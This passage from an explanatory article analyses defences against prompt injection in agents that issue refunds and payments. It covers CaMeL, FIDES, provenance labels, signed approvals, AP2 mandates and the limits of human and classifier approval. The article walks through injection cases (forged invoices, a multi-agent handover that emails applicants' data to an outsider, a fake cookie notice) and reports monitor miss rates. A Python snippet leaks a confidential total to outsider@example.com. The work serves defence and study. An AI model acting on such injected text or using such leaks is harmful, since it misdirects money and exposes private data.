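The ticket cannot add a second refund, because the privileged model finished writing the program before anything read the ticket. It cannot change the destination either, because the program specifies the original card. If the privileged model had mistakenly written the program to get the destination from the quarantined model, the account number would have been labelled untrusted, and a rule requiring a trusted destination would have blocked the call.

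The amount is harder to protect. The quarantined model might return £40, £90 or £900, and all three would have the same label because they come from the ticket. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives an example of a policy under which neither the recipient nor the amount of a payment may depend on untrusted data. This policy would block the £40 as well as the £90 and the £900. If the shop instead accepted untrusted amounts up to £100, the £90 would go through.

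The shop could reduce the risk by asking the quarantined model which item on the order was damaged and having the plugin look up the price. The policy would still have to let the choice of item depend on untrusted text, but an injection could at most obtain the price of another item the customer had bought.

Because CaMeL's plan is a program, other software can examine it before it runs. Nikolaou and colleagues' system builds a model of every path the plan could take and checks that model against rules. These rules can cover a whole task, whereas CaMeL's own policies apply to one call at a time. For example, the shop could require that a message to the customer follow every refund. The model simplifies loops, so the check may reject some safe plans.

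Labels do not replace limits on authority, because a £900 figure that Maya typed herself would have a trusted label even if it exceeded the limit. Surapani and colleagues want authority and origin tracked separately, so they would check both at each call.

### How FIDES differs

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, uses a planner that chooses one call at a time rather than writing the whole plan in advance. The planner sees any result that would leave the conversation's label unchanged, and FIDES replaces other data with placeholders. For Maya's ticket, the planner might see the order number and the date, with a placeholder for the customer's message.

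The planner can pass the placeholder to a quarantined model or open it and read the message. Opening it makes the whole conversation untrusted, and the policy then blocks consequential calls such as refunds. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) identify this choice as the main difference from CaMeL, whose plan cannot change in response to what the tools return. A CaMeL plan can contain branches, but the privileged model has to write them all beforehand.

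FIDES also lets the planner ask the quarantined model a yes-or-no question, such as whether the customer reports damage, and see only the answer. The label records that the answer is a single bit, and a policy may accept a bit from an untrusted source while refusing free text. One bit is too small to contain an instruction, but it can still be wrong, and a false "yes" could cost the shop £40. The size of a value is only a rough guide to the harm it can do, because an account number is also short and has a fixed format, yet with the wrong one a payment can go to anyone's account.

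Developers can now use FIDES outside research. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) announced the release of FIDES in May as part of Agent Framework, the company's toolkit for building agents.

### Security and completed tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The table shows how many injections succeeded and the percentage of tasks each agent completed when there was no attack. The injection counts exclude cases they thought AgentDojo had scored incorrectly.

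| Agent | Successful injections | Office | Travel | Banking | Team chat |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Undefended | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| One label for the whole conversation, with policies | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES with policies | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks on average than the agent with a single label, and 16 points more when both used o1, a stronger reasoning model. It still completed far fewer tasks than the undefended agent. Its security depends on the policies, since 21 injections succeeded without them.

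The zero depends on how the researchers labelled the data. AgentDojo has no labels of its own, so they marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. A real shop would not know in advance which fields an attacker might use. The result is good evidence that FIDES enforces its policies when the labels are right, but little evidence of how often a shop would get them right.

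In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) tested CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with GPT-5.2. CaMeL completed 66.7% of the tasks with its policies off and 37.5% with them on. One attack succeeded with the policies off and none with them on, although some of the attacked runs did not finish. The test has only 16 tasks, each run three times, so the completion rates are very uncertain. With a second model, MiMo-v2.5, the completion rate also dropped to 37.5% when the policies were on.

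That test has no undefended agent for comparison. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) includes one, using a version of AgentDojo in which a main agent passes work to specialised ones. Averaged over five models, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% when every agent used it. For GPT-4.1, the rate fell from 36.1% to 0.5%. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, though the researchers warn that attackers who adapt to their target have succeeded against every leading model in other tests.

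CaMeL ran without policies, so these results come from separating the two models. On AssetOpsBench, a set of professional tasks for teams of agents, the separation also lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models.

Kolluri and colleagues argue that such comparisons are unfair to defended agents. An undefended agent completes more tasks partly because the test lets it act without asking anyone, while many real products require a person to approve consequential actions. They therefore counted the tasks that agents finished with no human help. With o3-mini on AgentDojo, an agent that asked before every consequential action finished 24.3% of tasks without help, while FIDES finished 50.1%. Prudentia, their extension of FIDES that informs the planner of the labels and policies, finished 59.1%. Whether labels seem to make an agent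 less useful therefore depends on what it is compared with. If the shop's assistant would otherwise ask Maya about every refund, labels could save her time.

### "Pay the invoice in this email"

Suppose the shop's bookkeeper receives a courier's invoice and tells her assistant, "Pay the invoice in this email." The account number has to come from the email, which is untrusted. A rule that requires a trusted destination blocks the genuine invoice, while a rule that accepts destinations from emails also allows payment of a forged one. The genuine and forged account numbers have the same label, so no rule based only on origin can distinguish them.

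The two conditions that Siu and colleagues use to define an indirect prompt injection do not distinguish the invoices either, because neither invoice comes from an authenticated source and paying either one looks like what the bookkeeper asked for. Telling them apart requires knowing whether the account belongs to the courier.

AgentDojo contains tasks of this kind. Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori, whose planner can "endorse" data, or treat it as trusted despite its origin. The planner decides what to endorse before any untrusted data arrives. With its checks always on, Randori completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 and resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks across three models. In both failures, the user had asked it to read a file and pay as the file instructed, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request. Without endorsement,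 Randori blocks this attack but can't do what the user asked. CaMeL failed on the same kind of task in its original evaluation, and Debenedetti and colleagues had excluded such cases from the attacks it is meant to stop. Microsoft's relevant rule of thumb is that an attacker can make an agent do anything that a user's prompt can.

The shop has three ways to supply the missing fact or reduce the damage.

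| Answer | Decisions left to the email | Effect of a forged account number | Main cost |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Verified payee list | Which known supplier to pay, and how much | None | Somebody must verify each new supplier |
| Narrower delegation | The exact amount, up to a limit | None, if the user supplies the account or it is on record | The user must know more and type more |
| Question to the user | All the details, until she answers | The payment fails only if she notices | An interruption, and perhaps a phone call |

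With a verified payee list, the quarantined model extracts the supplier's name from the email, and the plugin finds the account in the shop's records. If a forged invoice names the real courier, the money goes to the real courier instead of the forger. A false invoice could still make the shop overpay a genuine supplier, so the list needs a limit on amounts too. The list also cannot help with a new supplier or one that has changed banks. As with any policy, the assistant must not be able to change the list.

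The bookkeeper could delegate more narrowly with the instruction "Pay Northway Couriers up to £200 for this invoice." She would then supply the payee and the maximum, and the email would supply only the exact amount and the reference. But Northway's name does not identify its account, so unless she also types the account number, it has to come from the payee list.

The assistant can ask the bookkeeper whether to trust the data or whether to make the payment. Kolluri and colleagues describe an email with a to-do list of ten items, each of which needs a protected call. The user can endorse the email once, which lets the agent do all ten, or approve each call separately. Endorsing the email is quicker, but it covers calls the user has not yet seen. For one invoice, endorsing the data saves no questions, so the assistant should ask about the payment itself and show the amount and account number.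 The bookkeeper's answer is useful only if she can check the account number against something other than the email, for example by phoning the courier on a number from an earlier contract.

The payee list is the best default of the three because it does not rely on anyone noticing a wrong digit. Labels show when the list is not enough. A payment to an account from the shop's records can go ahead within the limit, but somebody has to verify an account that comes from the email. Maya would face the same problem if a customer's card had closed and he asked for his refund to go to a new account. The shop has no list of customers' bank accounts, so she would have to confirm the number through the contact details already on his record.

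### Labels lost between agents and plugins

All the attacks that got past CaMeL in Peters-Gill and colleagues' test exploited the handover between agents. In their demonstration, a user asks for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack. One agent reads the applicant database, which contains an injected instruction, and the main agent puts the summary into a message to a notification agent. Each agent uses CaMeL correctly, but the notification agent treats the message as its user's request. Its privileged model therefore reads the injected text and writes a plan that also emails the applicants' details to an outsider.

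They prove that this weakness is general. If a system has more than one agent and at least one tool that returns untrusted data, and agents can freely pass on what their tools return, then some user request will let that data shape another agent's plan. To prevent this, they split each handover into an instruction, which the receiving planner reads, and a set of variables, which it does not. The interpreter refuses any instruction that contains data from a tool. With this change, no attack succeeded, but the completion rate on AssetOpsBench fell by a further 3.2 points on average.

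Storage can remove labels in the same way. Suppose the ticket plugin copies the account number from a ticket into the customer's record. When the record plugin later returns the number as the shop's own data, a rule that requires a trusted destination lets it through. To prevent this, the database would have to store the label with the number. FIDES expects labels in a metadata field of each tool's result, and Costa and colleagues wrote wrappers around AgentDojo's tools to add them. A shop that uses other companies' plugins would probably have to write its own wrappers or treat everything those plugins return as untrusted.

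The original labels can also be wrong. Costa and colleagues infer who may read an email from its sender and recipients, although somebody may have shared it more widely. They also suggest that a system might relabel an untrusted document as trusted after a detector finds no injection in it. This would allow more tasks, but the label would be only as reliable as the detector.

### Leaks through the choices a program makes

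Tracking data is difficult even inside one program. Garby and colleagues found that when a program inserted an untrusted value into a longer piece of text, CaMeL's interpreter treated the resulting text as trusted. If the shop's plan built the destination by putting "acct_" in front of a number from the ticket, that destination could pass a rule meant to block it.

They also found that secrets could escape through steps that a program skips. This version of their example uses an order total that the shop wants to keep confidential:

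```python
big_spender = True
flag = True
if order.total > 1000:
    flag = False
if flag:
    big_spender = False
if big_spender:
    send_email("outsider@example.com", "yes")
```

If the total is above 1,000, `flag` becomes false and confidential. The program then skips the line that would change `big_spender`, which stays true and keeps its public label, so CaMeL allows the email. If the total is lower, no email goes out. The outsider therefore learns whether the total is above 1,000, although no message contains a confidential value. CaMeL also retries failed programs in a loop that its labels do not cover. Each attempt reveals one bit by showing whether a policy blocked it, and repeated attempts could reveal a whole secret.

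An attacker would struggle to get such a program written, because CaMeL's privileged model does not read untrusted text. The flaws matter more if that model makes a mistake or has been misled by another route. *Operationalizing CaMeL* attributes part of the difficulty to Python, whose handling of types and errors makes strong guarantees hard to establish. Garby and colleagues instead designed a small language and gave a computer-checked proof that its interpreter rules out this class of flaw. FIDES deliberately does not prevent leaks through a program's choices, because Costa and colleagues judged that preventing them would stop an agent from writing anything public once it had read anything secret.

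Untrusted data can also steer a program towards a harmful step that it already contains. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL to agents that operate a computer through its screen. The planner has to prepare for many situations, such as a cookie notice that covers a web page. The researchers put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement, and the agent clicked it and went to the attacker's site. The plan included the click, but the attacker had chosen its target. A refund plan that pays when goods arrive damaged has the same weakness, because a customer can lie about the damage. Shops already had this problem before they used assistants, and provenance does not solve it.

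### Hostile text from a trusted user

CaMeL, FIDES and Prudentia all treat tool descriptions and the user's own message as trusted. However, PromptArmor found that developers often rewrite tool descriptions after users have approved a connector.

Maya can break the assumption by accident. If she copies the whole ticket into the chat box and types "deal with this" above it, the privileged model reads the ticket as part of her request. It may then write a plan that pays £900 to the account in the ticket, and the amount and the account will both have trusted labels. The client could label pasted text as untrusted, but people also paste text that they want the assistant to follow, such as a list of instructions from a manager. Maya's £100 limit and the rule about the original card would still block the £900 payment, but a pasted request for £90 to the original card would pass those checks and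 the label check.

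## When does a user's confirmation authorise an action?

Maya's limit and provenance labels can both miss the unrequested £90 refund, but the assistant can still ask her before it pays. Her "yes" authorises the refund if four conditions hold:

1. She has the authority to approve it.
2. She sees its actual effect, including the amount and the destination.
3. Ordinary code, not the model, writes the screen she sees.
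4. The call that runs is exactly the one she approved.

Suppose the assistant writes, "I've reviewed the ticket and prepared the refund. Continue?" Maya expects to pay £40 to the original card, so she clicks "Yes", and £900 goes to the other account. None of the conditions held. The refund was above her limit. The message left out the amount and the payee, and it came from a model that had read the attacker's text. Nothing connected her click to a particular call.

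A better prompt takes each line from the call itself or from the shop's records:

```text
Refund          £900.00 on order A-1182
Pay to          account ending 1234
Card on order   ending 7781 (will receive nothing)
Account source  customer's message in ticket T-730

[Refuse]   [Approve]
```

Maya can now see that the money would go to the wrong place. The client can show the last line only if it tracks where values come from. The prompt should show any free-text argument, such as a reason for the refund, as a quotation, because the ticket's author could have written "already approved by your manager".

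Maya's approval can't raise her limit, so the plugin shouldn't show her an "Approve" button for the £900 refund. It should refuse the call or send the approval prompt to a manager who is authorised to approve that amount and choose where the refund goes.

According to Anthropic, allowing an action in Claude never grants more access than the person has in the connected service. This holds when each person signs in with their own account, but a custom connector that uses a shared credential, such as a shop's payment key, can access whatever that credential allows.

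### Binding an approval to one call

A good confirmation prompt is not enough if the program records only that the user said yes, without recording what they approved. Suppose a user approves a £40 refund and the client sets `approved = true` for the session. The next call, for £900, carries the same flag, so it also counts as approved.

The shop can prevent this by having the approval page sign the details:

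approval = sign(*K*, [user, operation, order, amount, destination, expiry time, one-time number])

The confirmation page signs the details of the action with a secret key that neither the model nor the client can use. The refund plugin verifies the signature, compares the signed details with the call, and stores the one-time number so that nobody can use the approval twice. If the amount changes from 40 to 900 after the user clicks to approve, the comparison fails.

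European law already requires something similar, called dynamic linking, for many online payments. *Security measures for the application of strong customer authentication*, a chapter of a 2018 EU regulation, requires the payment provider to make the payer aware of the amount and the payee. The authentication code must be specific to both, and changing either must invalidate it. The provider must also protect the information on the payer's screen, because a correct code does little good if an attacker can alter what the payer reads. The FCA's *Strong Customer Authentication and Common and Secure Methods of Communication* contains the British version, with nearly the same wording.

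OneSpan's *Performing dynamic linking in a compliant, convenient way* describes how a banking app can tie a customer's confirmation to a single transaction. The customer opens a notification, the app shows the transaction, and she authenticates with a fingerprint or a face scan. Her phone then calculates a code from the transaction data and sends it to the bank. Barclaycard gives the example of a fraudster who intercepts a £100 payment and changes it to £1,000 for a different recipient. With dynamic linking, the code for the original payment doesn't work for the altered one.

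The code shows that somebody with the customer's phone and fingerprint approved this amount for this payee, but not that the payee is owed the money. If the shop's bookkeeper approves a forged courier invoice, the bank receives a valid code for a payment to the forger's account.

### Signed mandates for purchases by agents

The Agent Payments Protocol (AP2), which Google introduced in 2025, applies the same idea to shopping by AI agents. Google has since donated it to the FIDO Alliance, an industry association that develops open standards (Google, *We're donating Agent Payments Protocol to the FIDO Alliance*).

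The current version, AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)*, uses signed records called mandates. When the user is present, a purchase works like this:

1. The agent assembles a cart, and the merchant signs the resulting checkout, which contains the items and the price.
2. The agent prepares a Checkout Mandate and a Payment Mandate. Each contains a hash of the checkout, a short code that changes if anything in the checkout changes.
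3. A "Trusted Surface", a screen that no language model may run, shows the contents to the user and obtains her approval and the signatures.
4. The company that supplies the payment credential verifies the Payment Mandate, and the merchant verifies the Checkout Mandate.

If the user will be away, she approves "open" mandates beforehand. These specify constraints, such as a range of amounts and a list of permitted payees, and the key of the agent that may use them. The agent later signs "closed" mandates for a specific purchase, and the companies that receive them check the purchase against the constraints.

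| Signature | What it proves | What it leaves open |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Merchant's, on the checkout | The merchant offered these items at this price | Whether the description is true |
| User's, on a closed Checkout Mandate | She approved this cart | Whether the agent passed over a better one |
| User's, on a closed Payment Mandate | She approved this payment for this cart | Whether the goods will arrive |
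| User's, on an open mandate | She approved these limits for this agent | Which purchase she would have chosen |
| Agent's, on a closed mandate | The agent with the named key chose this purchase | Whether the user would agree with the choice |

AP2 accepts signatures from the user or from an approved company that provides the agent. When the company signs, the merchant relies on it to have asked the user. Aviv, Gandh and colleagues (2026) add in *Beyond the Mandate* that the screen must show the mandate faithfully and that each recipient must do its own checks.

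A user's signature is weaker evidence of intent than an earlier description of AP2 claimed when it called the signature "non-repudiable proof of their intent". Aviv and colleagues point out that an attacker doesn't have to forge a mandate if he can manipulate the product data or messages the agent reads before anyone signs. *Signing the Transaction but Not the Decision* (Louck, Dvir and Stulman, 2026) found that one false statement about stock in a product description could lead an agent to choose a more expensive item. The cart still matched the merchant's listing and passed every check. A user who is present can refuse that cart, but she may not know that a cheaper item was available.

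Constraints limit the damage only if a developer sets them. Louck and colleagues found that AP2's sample agent for purchases with the user present included no constraints.

AP2 covers purchases, so the shop can't use it for Maya's refund. The shop could copy AP2's two forms of approval, with a closed one for a single refund and an open one for routine refunds within fixed limits.

### How current products ask for approval

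In 2023, OpenAI removed the Chat with Code plugin because it acted without asking the user for confirmation. By late 2026, the main products let users or administrators choose how often the product asks for confirmation, and several let a model answer in the user's place.

| Product | Routine actions | When a person decides |
| --- | --- | --- |
| ChatGPT apps | Run without asking if the permission setting allows them | Higher-risk actions under most settings, and every financial transaction through a plugin |
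| Claude connectors | Run without asking if the organisation chose "Always allow" | Tools marked "Needs approval" |
| Claude in Chrome | An automatic check reviews them by default in the newer side panel | Granting authorisations, changing permissions, entering sensitive data |
| Claude Code | An automatic check reviews many of them by default | Actions covered by an "ask" rule, or after repeated blocks |
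| Codex, OpenAI's coding agent | Run inside a restricted environment | Requests to go outside it, unless another agent reviews them |

OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* lists four settings: "Always ask", "Allow read actions", "Allow low-risk actions" and "Allow all actions". "Allow low-risk actions" is the default. OpenAI says an action needs more review if it can affect another service, expose sensitive information or be hard to undo, so any refund would need more review. The approval card describes the app and the proposed action, but the guide doesn't mention showing where each value in the action came from.

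ChatGPT is stricter with plugins that trade assets. OpenAI's *Connected apps in ChatGPT* requires a separate confirmation for each transaction, on a screen that the financial company controls. This nearly meets the second and third conditions, since the company that will execute the trade also shows it to the user.

For Claude's connectors, an organisation sets each tool to "Always allow", "Needs approval" or "Blocked". The setting applies to the whole tool, so "Needs approval" on `issue_refund` produces a prompt for a £4 refund as well as a £900 one. However, the prompt may not appear in auto mode, where a model reviews actions instead of the user. Hartherz (2026) reports in *Claude*, a developer's note, that the setting counts as permission in that mode. This is one person's observation, but a shop that relies on the setting should test it.

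Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome permissions guide* forbids purchases and other financial transactions in every mode, so Claude should not issue even the £40 refund through a web page. In the guide, "Skip all approvals" is the new name for "Act without asking", the mode in which a faked click could start a task unprompted.

Coding agents have moved furthest from asking the user to confirm each action. When Anthropic introduced auto mode in March 2026, Claude Code still asked by default before every file write and shell command (an instruction typed to the operating system), according to Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code*. Auto mode is now the default for interactive sessions. Codex starts with network access off and a sandbox that usually confines it to the current project, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. To leave the sandbox, it asks the user or, under OpenAI's *Auto-review*,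 a separate agent. OpenAI uses a separate agent because one trained to finish the task is under pressure to treat the need for approval as another obstacle.

### How often people catch a dangerous action

Most of the published figures on approval come from Anthropic and concern Claude Code. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users accepted 93% of approval prompts, and its later *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) put the figure at 97%. Most of the commands were probably safe, so these rates don't prove that users were careless. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents, but they may reject a plan because it is bad rather than dangerous.

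An experiment gives more direct evidence. Anthropic had 1,053 paid professional testers recruited for a coding study in a test environment. They knew they were being evaluated but not for what. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time, while auto mode blocked 89% of the same commands. Anthropic's totals give this breakdown:

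| | Auto mode blocked | Auto mode allowed |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

Requiring both the testers and the automatic check to approve each command would have stopped 943 commands (89.6%), only six more than the automatic check alone.

The testers became less careful as sessions went on, refusing about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Maya would pass 50 prompts in a day if she handled 60 refunds with a prompt for each. But fatigue explains only part of the result. Even early in a session the testers missed about five out of six dangerous commands, so showing fewer prompts would not have been enough to solve the problem.

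Maya might do better than the testers, because they had none of their own code at stake and a shell command is harder to read than an amount and a payee. But she might also do worse, because they were professionals and the commands were clearly dangerous, whereas a £90 refund looks ordinary. The experiment didn't test payment prompts, so its 13.6% figure is a reason for the shop to be concerned, but the shop can't use it to predict how Maya will respond.

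Anthropic also compared real sessions from May and June 2026 that its safety systems had flagged. A model graded the harm in each. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for appeared in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own mode, so differences in their work may explain some of the gap.

### What an automatic check can replace

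Auto mode's classifier, a second model, receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations and the tools' results so that neither can bias the classifier toward approval. In Anthropic's earlier tests, the classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary calls from employees and missed 17% of 52 real cases in which the agent had gone beyond what the user wanted. With so few cases, the true miss rate could plausibly be from 9% to 30%.

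In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier recognised that the action was dangerous but wrongly concluded that the user had authorised it. For example, one user said "Clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change), and the classifier treated this as permission to run a command that overwrites the project's history. Anthropic calls such remarks "approval-shaped evidence".

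A classifier of this kind would also have too little information to assess the call in Maya's case. Its input would include "Deal with this ticket" and a call for £40 or £90, but not the ticket itself, so it couldn't determine which amount the customer was owed. If it were set to block uncertain calls, it would block both. Adding the ticket to its input would supply the missing facts, but would also let the ticket's author try to manipulate its decision.

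Automatic review can still reduce the harm from injections. Anthropic commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 hidden-instruction attacks ten times each, and none succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. Little of this was due to automatic review, because attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09% of the time on average without it. Review made more difference for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, where attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% with Auto-review. OpenAI has since updated Auto-review, so the 5.83% figure may be out of date.

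### Confirm every sensitive action, or ask less often?

Some people want a confirmation for every sensitive action because a single mistake can do serious harm. A payment to a stranger's account may be impossible to recover, and only the user knows whether she wanted it. OpenAI takes this position in its rule for financial plugins. Anthropic does too for some work. It recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves, and it warns in its current documentation that auto mode "does not guarantee safety".

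The case against asking users to confirm every action is that people stop reading prompts they see all day. Vorwerck (2026) adds in *Running auto mode in production* that reviewing every command becomes a bottleneck when sessions last hours or run in parallel. A ChatGPT user makes the same complaint about ordinary office work in *Trusted approval policy for repeated connector write actions*. He always approves changes to his planning notes and asks for a way to allow them for 30 minutes or permanently.

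Anthropic's experiment supports the second side on routine commands. It provides much less evidence about rare payments with a clear prompt, where the first side's case is strongest. The two positions are compatible if few enough actions count as "sensitive", and the shop has three ways to keep that number down.

| Method | What Maya sees | Treatment of the unrequested £90 | Main weakness |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
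| By risk | A prompt for any refund above £20 or to a new account | She has to approve it | Attackers can stay below £20 |
| By batch | One list of refunds, twice a day | It is one line among many | Customers wait, and she may skim |
| By standing rule | Nothing, if the refund fits the rule | Refused or sent to her if the rule stops at £20 | The rule may be too broad |

Basing approval on risk works best when fixed facts determine the risk, such as the amount and whether the destination is new. OpenAI does this with network access for its own use of Codex, allowing expected destinations, blocking unwanted ones and requiring approval for unfamiliar ones. If the assistant's model rated the risk of each refund instead, text in a ticket could influence the rating. Even with fixed criteria, the shop would need a daily total to catch a series of £19 refunds.

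If Maya approves refunds in a batch, she makes one decision instead of thirty and can compare similar refunds side by side. However, a batch approval is harder to bind to the exact refunds she saw. The European rule requires a batch's code to be specific to the total amount and the payees, but doesn't mention the amount for each payee. If the shop owed one customer £40 and another £10, someone could swap the two amounts without changing the total or the payees. The shop's approval should therefore cover every line. Long lists create another difficulty, and *Dynamic linking for batch transactions*, a question submitted to the European Banking Authority, asks whether the payer has to be made aware of every payee.

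A standing rule removes the prompt, so its wording must exclude the actions Maya would have refused. Users tend to write such rules too broadly. By Anthropic's count, as of June 2026, 5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had created a rule that allowed any shell command, and another 43% had rules that were nearly as broad. Auto mode now ignores those rules while it is on. For refunds, the shop can write the rule itself, such as the earlier allowance of £20 per order, and keep it in the plugin, where Maya can't widen it.
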